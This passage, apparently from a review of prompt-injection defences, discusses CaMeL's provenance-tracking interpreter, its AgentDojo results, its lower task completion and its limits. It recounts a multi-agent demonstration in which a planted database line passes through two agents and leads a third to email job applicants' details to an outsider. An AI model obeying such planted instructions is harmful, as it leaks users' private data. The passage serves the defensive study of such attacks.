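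CaMeL deals with this by running the program in an interpreter that records where each value came from and who may read it. Before a tool runs, the interpreter checks these records against a security policy. Here the records would show that the address came from an email, so the interpreter would block the message or ask the user, unless the address is on a trusted list.

Agents complete fewer tasks with this protection. Tallam and Miller report that CaMeL completed 67% of tasks in its original evaluation on AgentDojo, a benchmark of everyday tasks with attacks planted in the data. *SecureClaw* (2026), a paper on a competing system, reports a later run in which none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but it completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks, compared with 59 for SecureClaw.

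The choice of model probably explains part of the difference. *MetaPermit* (2026) examines 5,581 cases in which CaMeL blocked the attack but left the user's task unfinished. In 4,706 of them, the model made at most two tool calls and then stopped with a message. It usually fetched the information but never completed the program that would have used it.

Peters-Gill and colleagues tested CaMeL with five models in systems where one agent delegates work to others. On a benchmark of professional tasks, CaMeL lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. On a version of AgentDojo adapted to several agents, it cut the average attack success rate from 12.9% to 0.2%. Nearly all of that gain came from two older models. Without CaMeL, attacks succeeded only 1.5% of the time on Fable 5 and never on GPT-5.5.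 Blocking these fixed attacks is therefore a weaker reason to use CaMeL with a strong model than protecting against attacks nobody has tried yet.

The remaining 0.2% exposed a gap in how agents communicate. In one demonstration, Peters-Gill and colleagues asked a system of three CaMeL agents to send a colleague a summary of job applicants over Slack. A planted line in the database passed through the first two agents as data. The coordinating agent then included the summary in its instruction to the third agent. The third agent treated the planted line as part of the user's request and emailed the applicants' details to an outsider. When the agents sent instructions and data to each other through separate channels, no attack in the benchmark succeeded.

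The CaMeL paper states that prompt injection is "not fully solved", mainly because someone has to write and maintain the policies, and users can tire of approving exceptions. Tallam and Miller add that using two models roughly doubles the number of model calls. They also point out that CaMeL trusts the user's request, so an attacker who tricks the user into pasting text there can still influence the plan.

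This is consistent with OWASP's claim, which concerns prevention inside the model. CaMeL's quarantined model can still be fooled, and the software around it provides the protection. If the interpreter works correctly and the user's request is honest, CaMeL guarantees that no wording in an email can add an action to the plan. This disproves any broader claim that developers can only make successful attacks less likely.

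The guarantee covers only actions, so a planted email can still produce a false summary. It also depends on knowing the plan in advance. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Willison (2025) describes a paper by 11 researchers who openly accept this limit and gain security by preventing agents from solving arbitrary tasks. An assistant built this way can send Dana a file, but it can't safely "do whatever Dana's email asks", because the plan would then have to come from the email.
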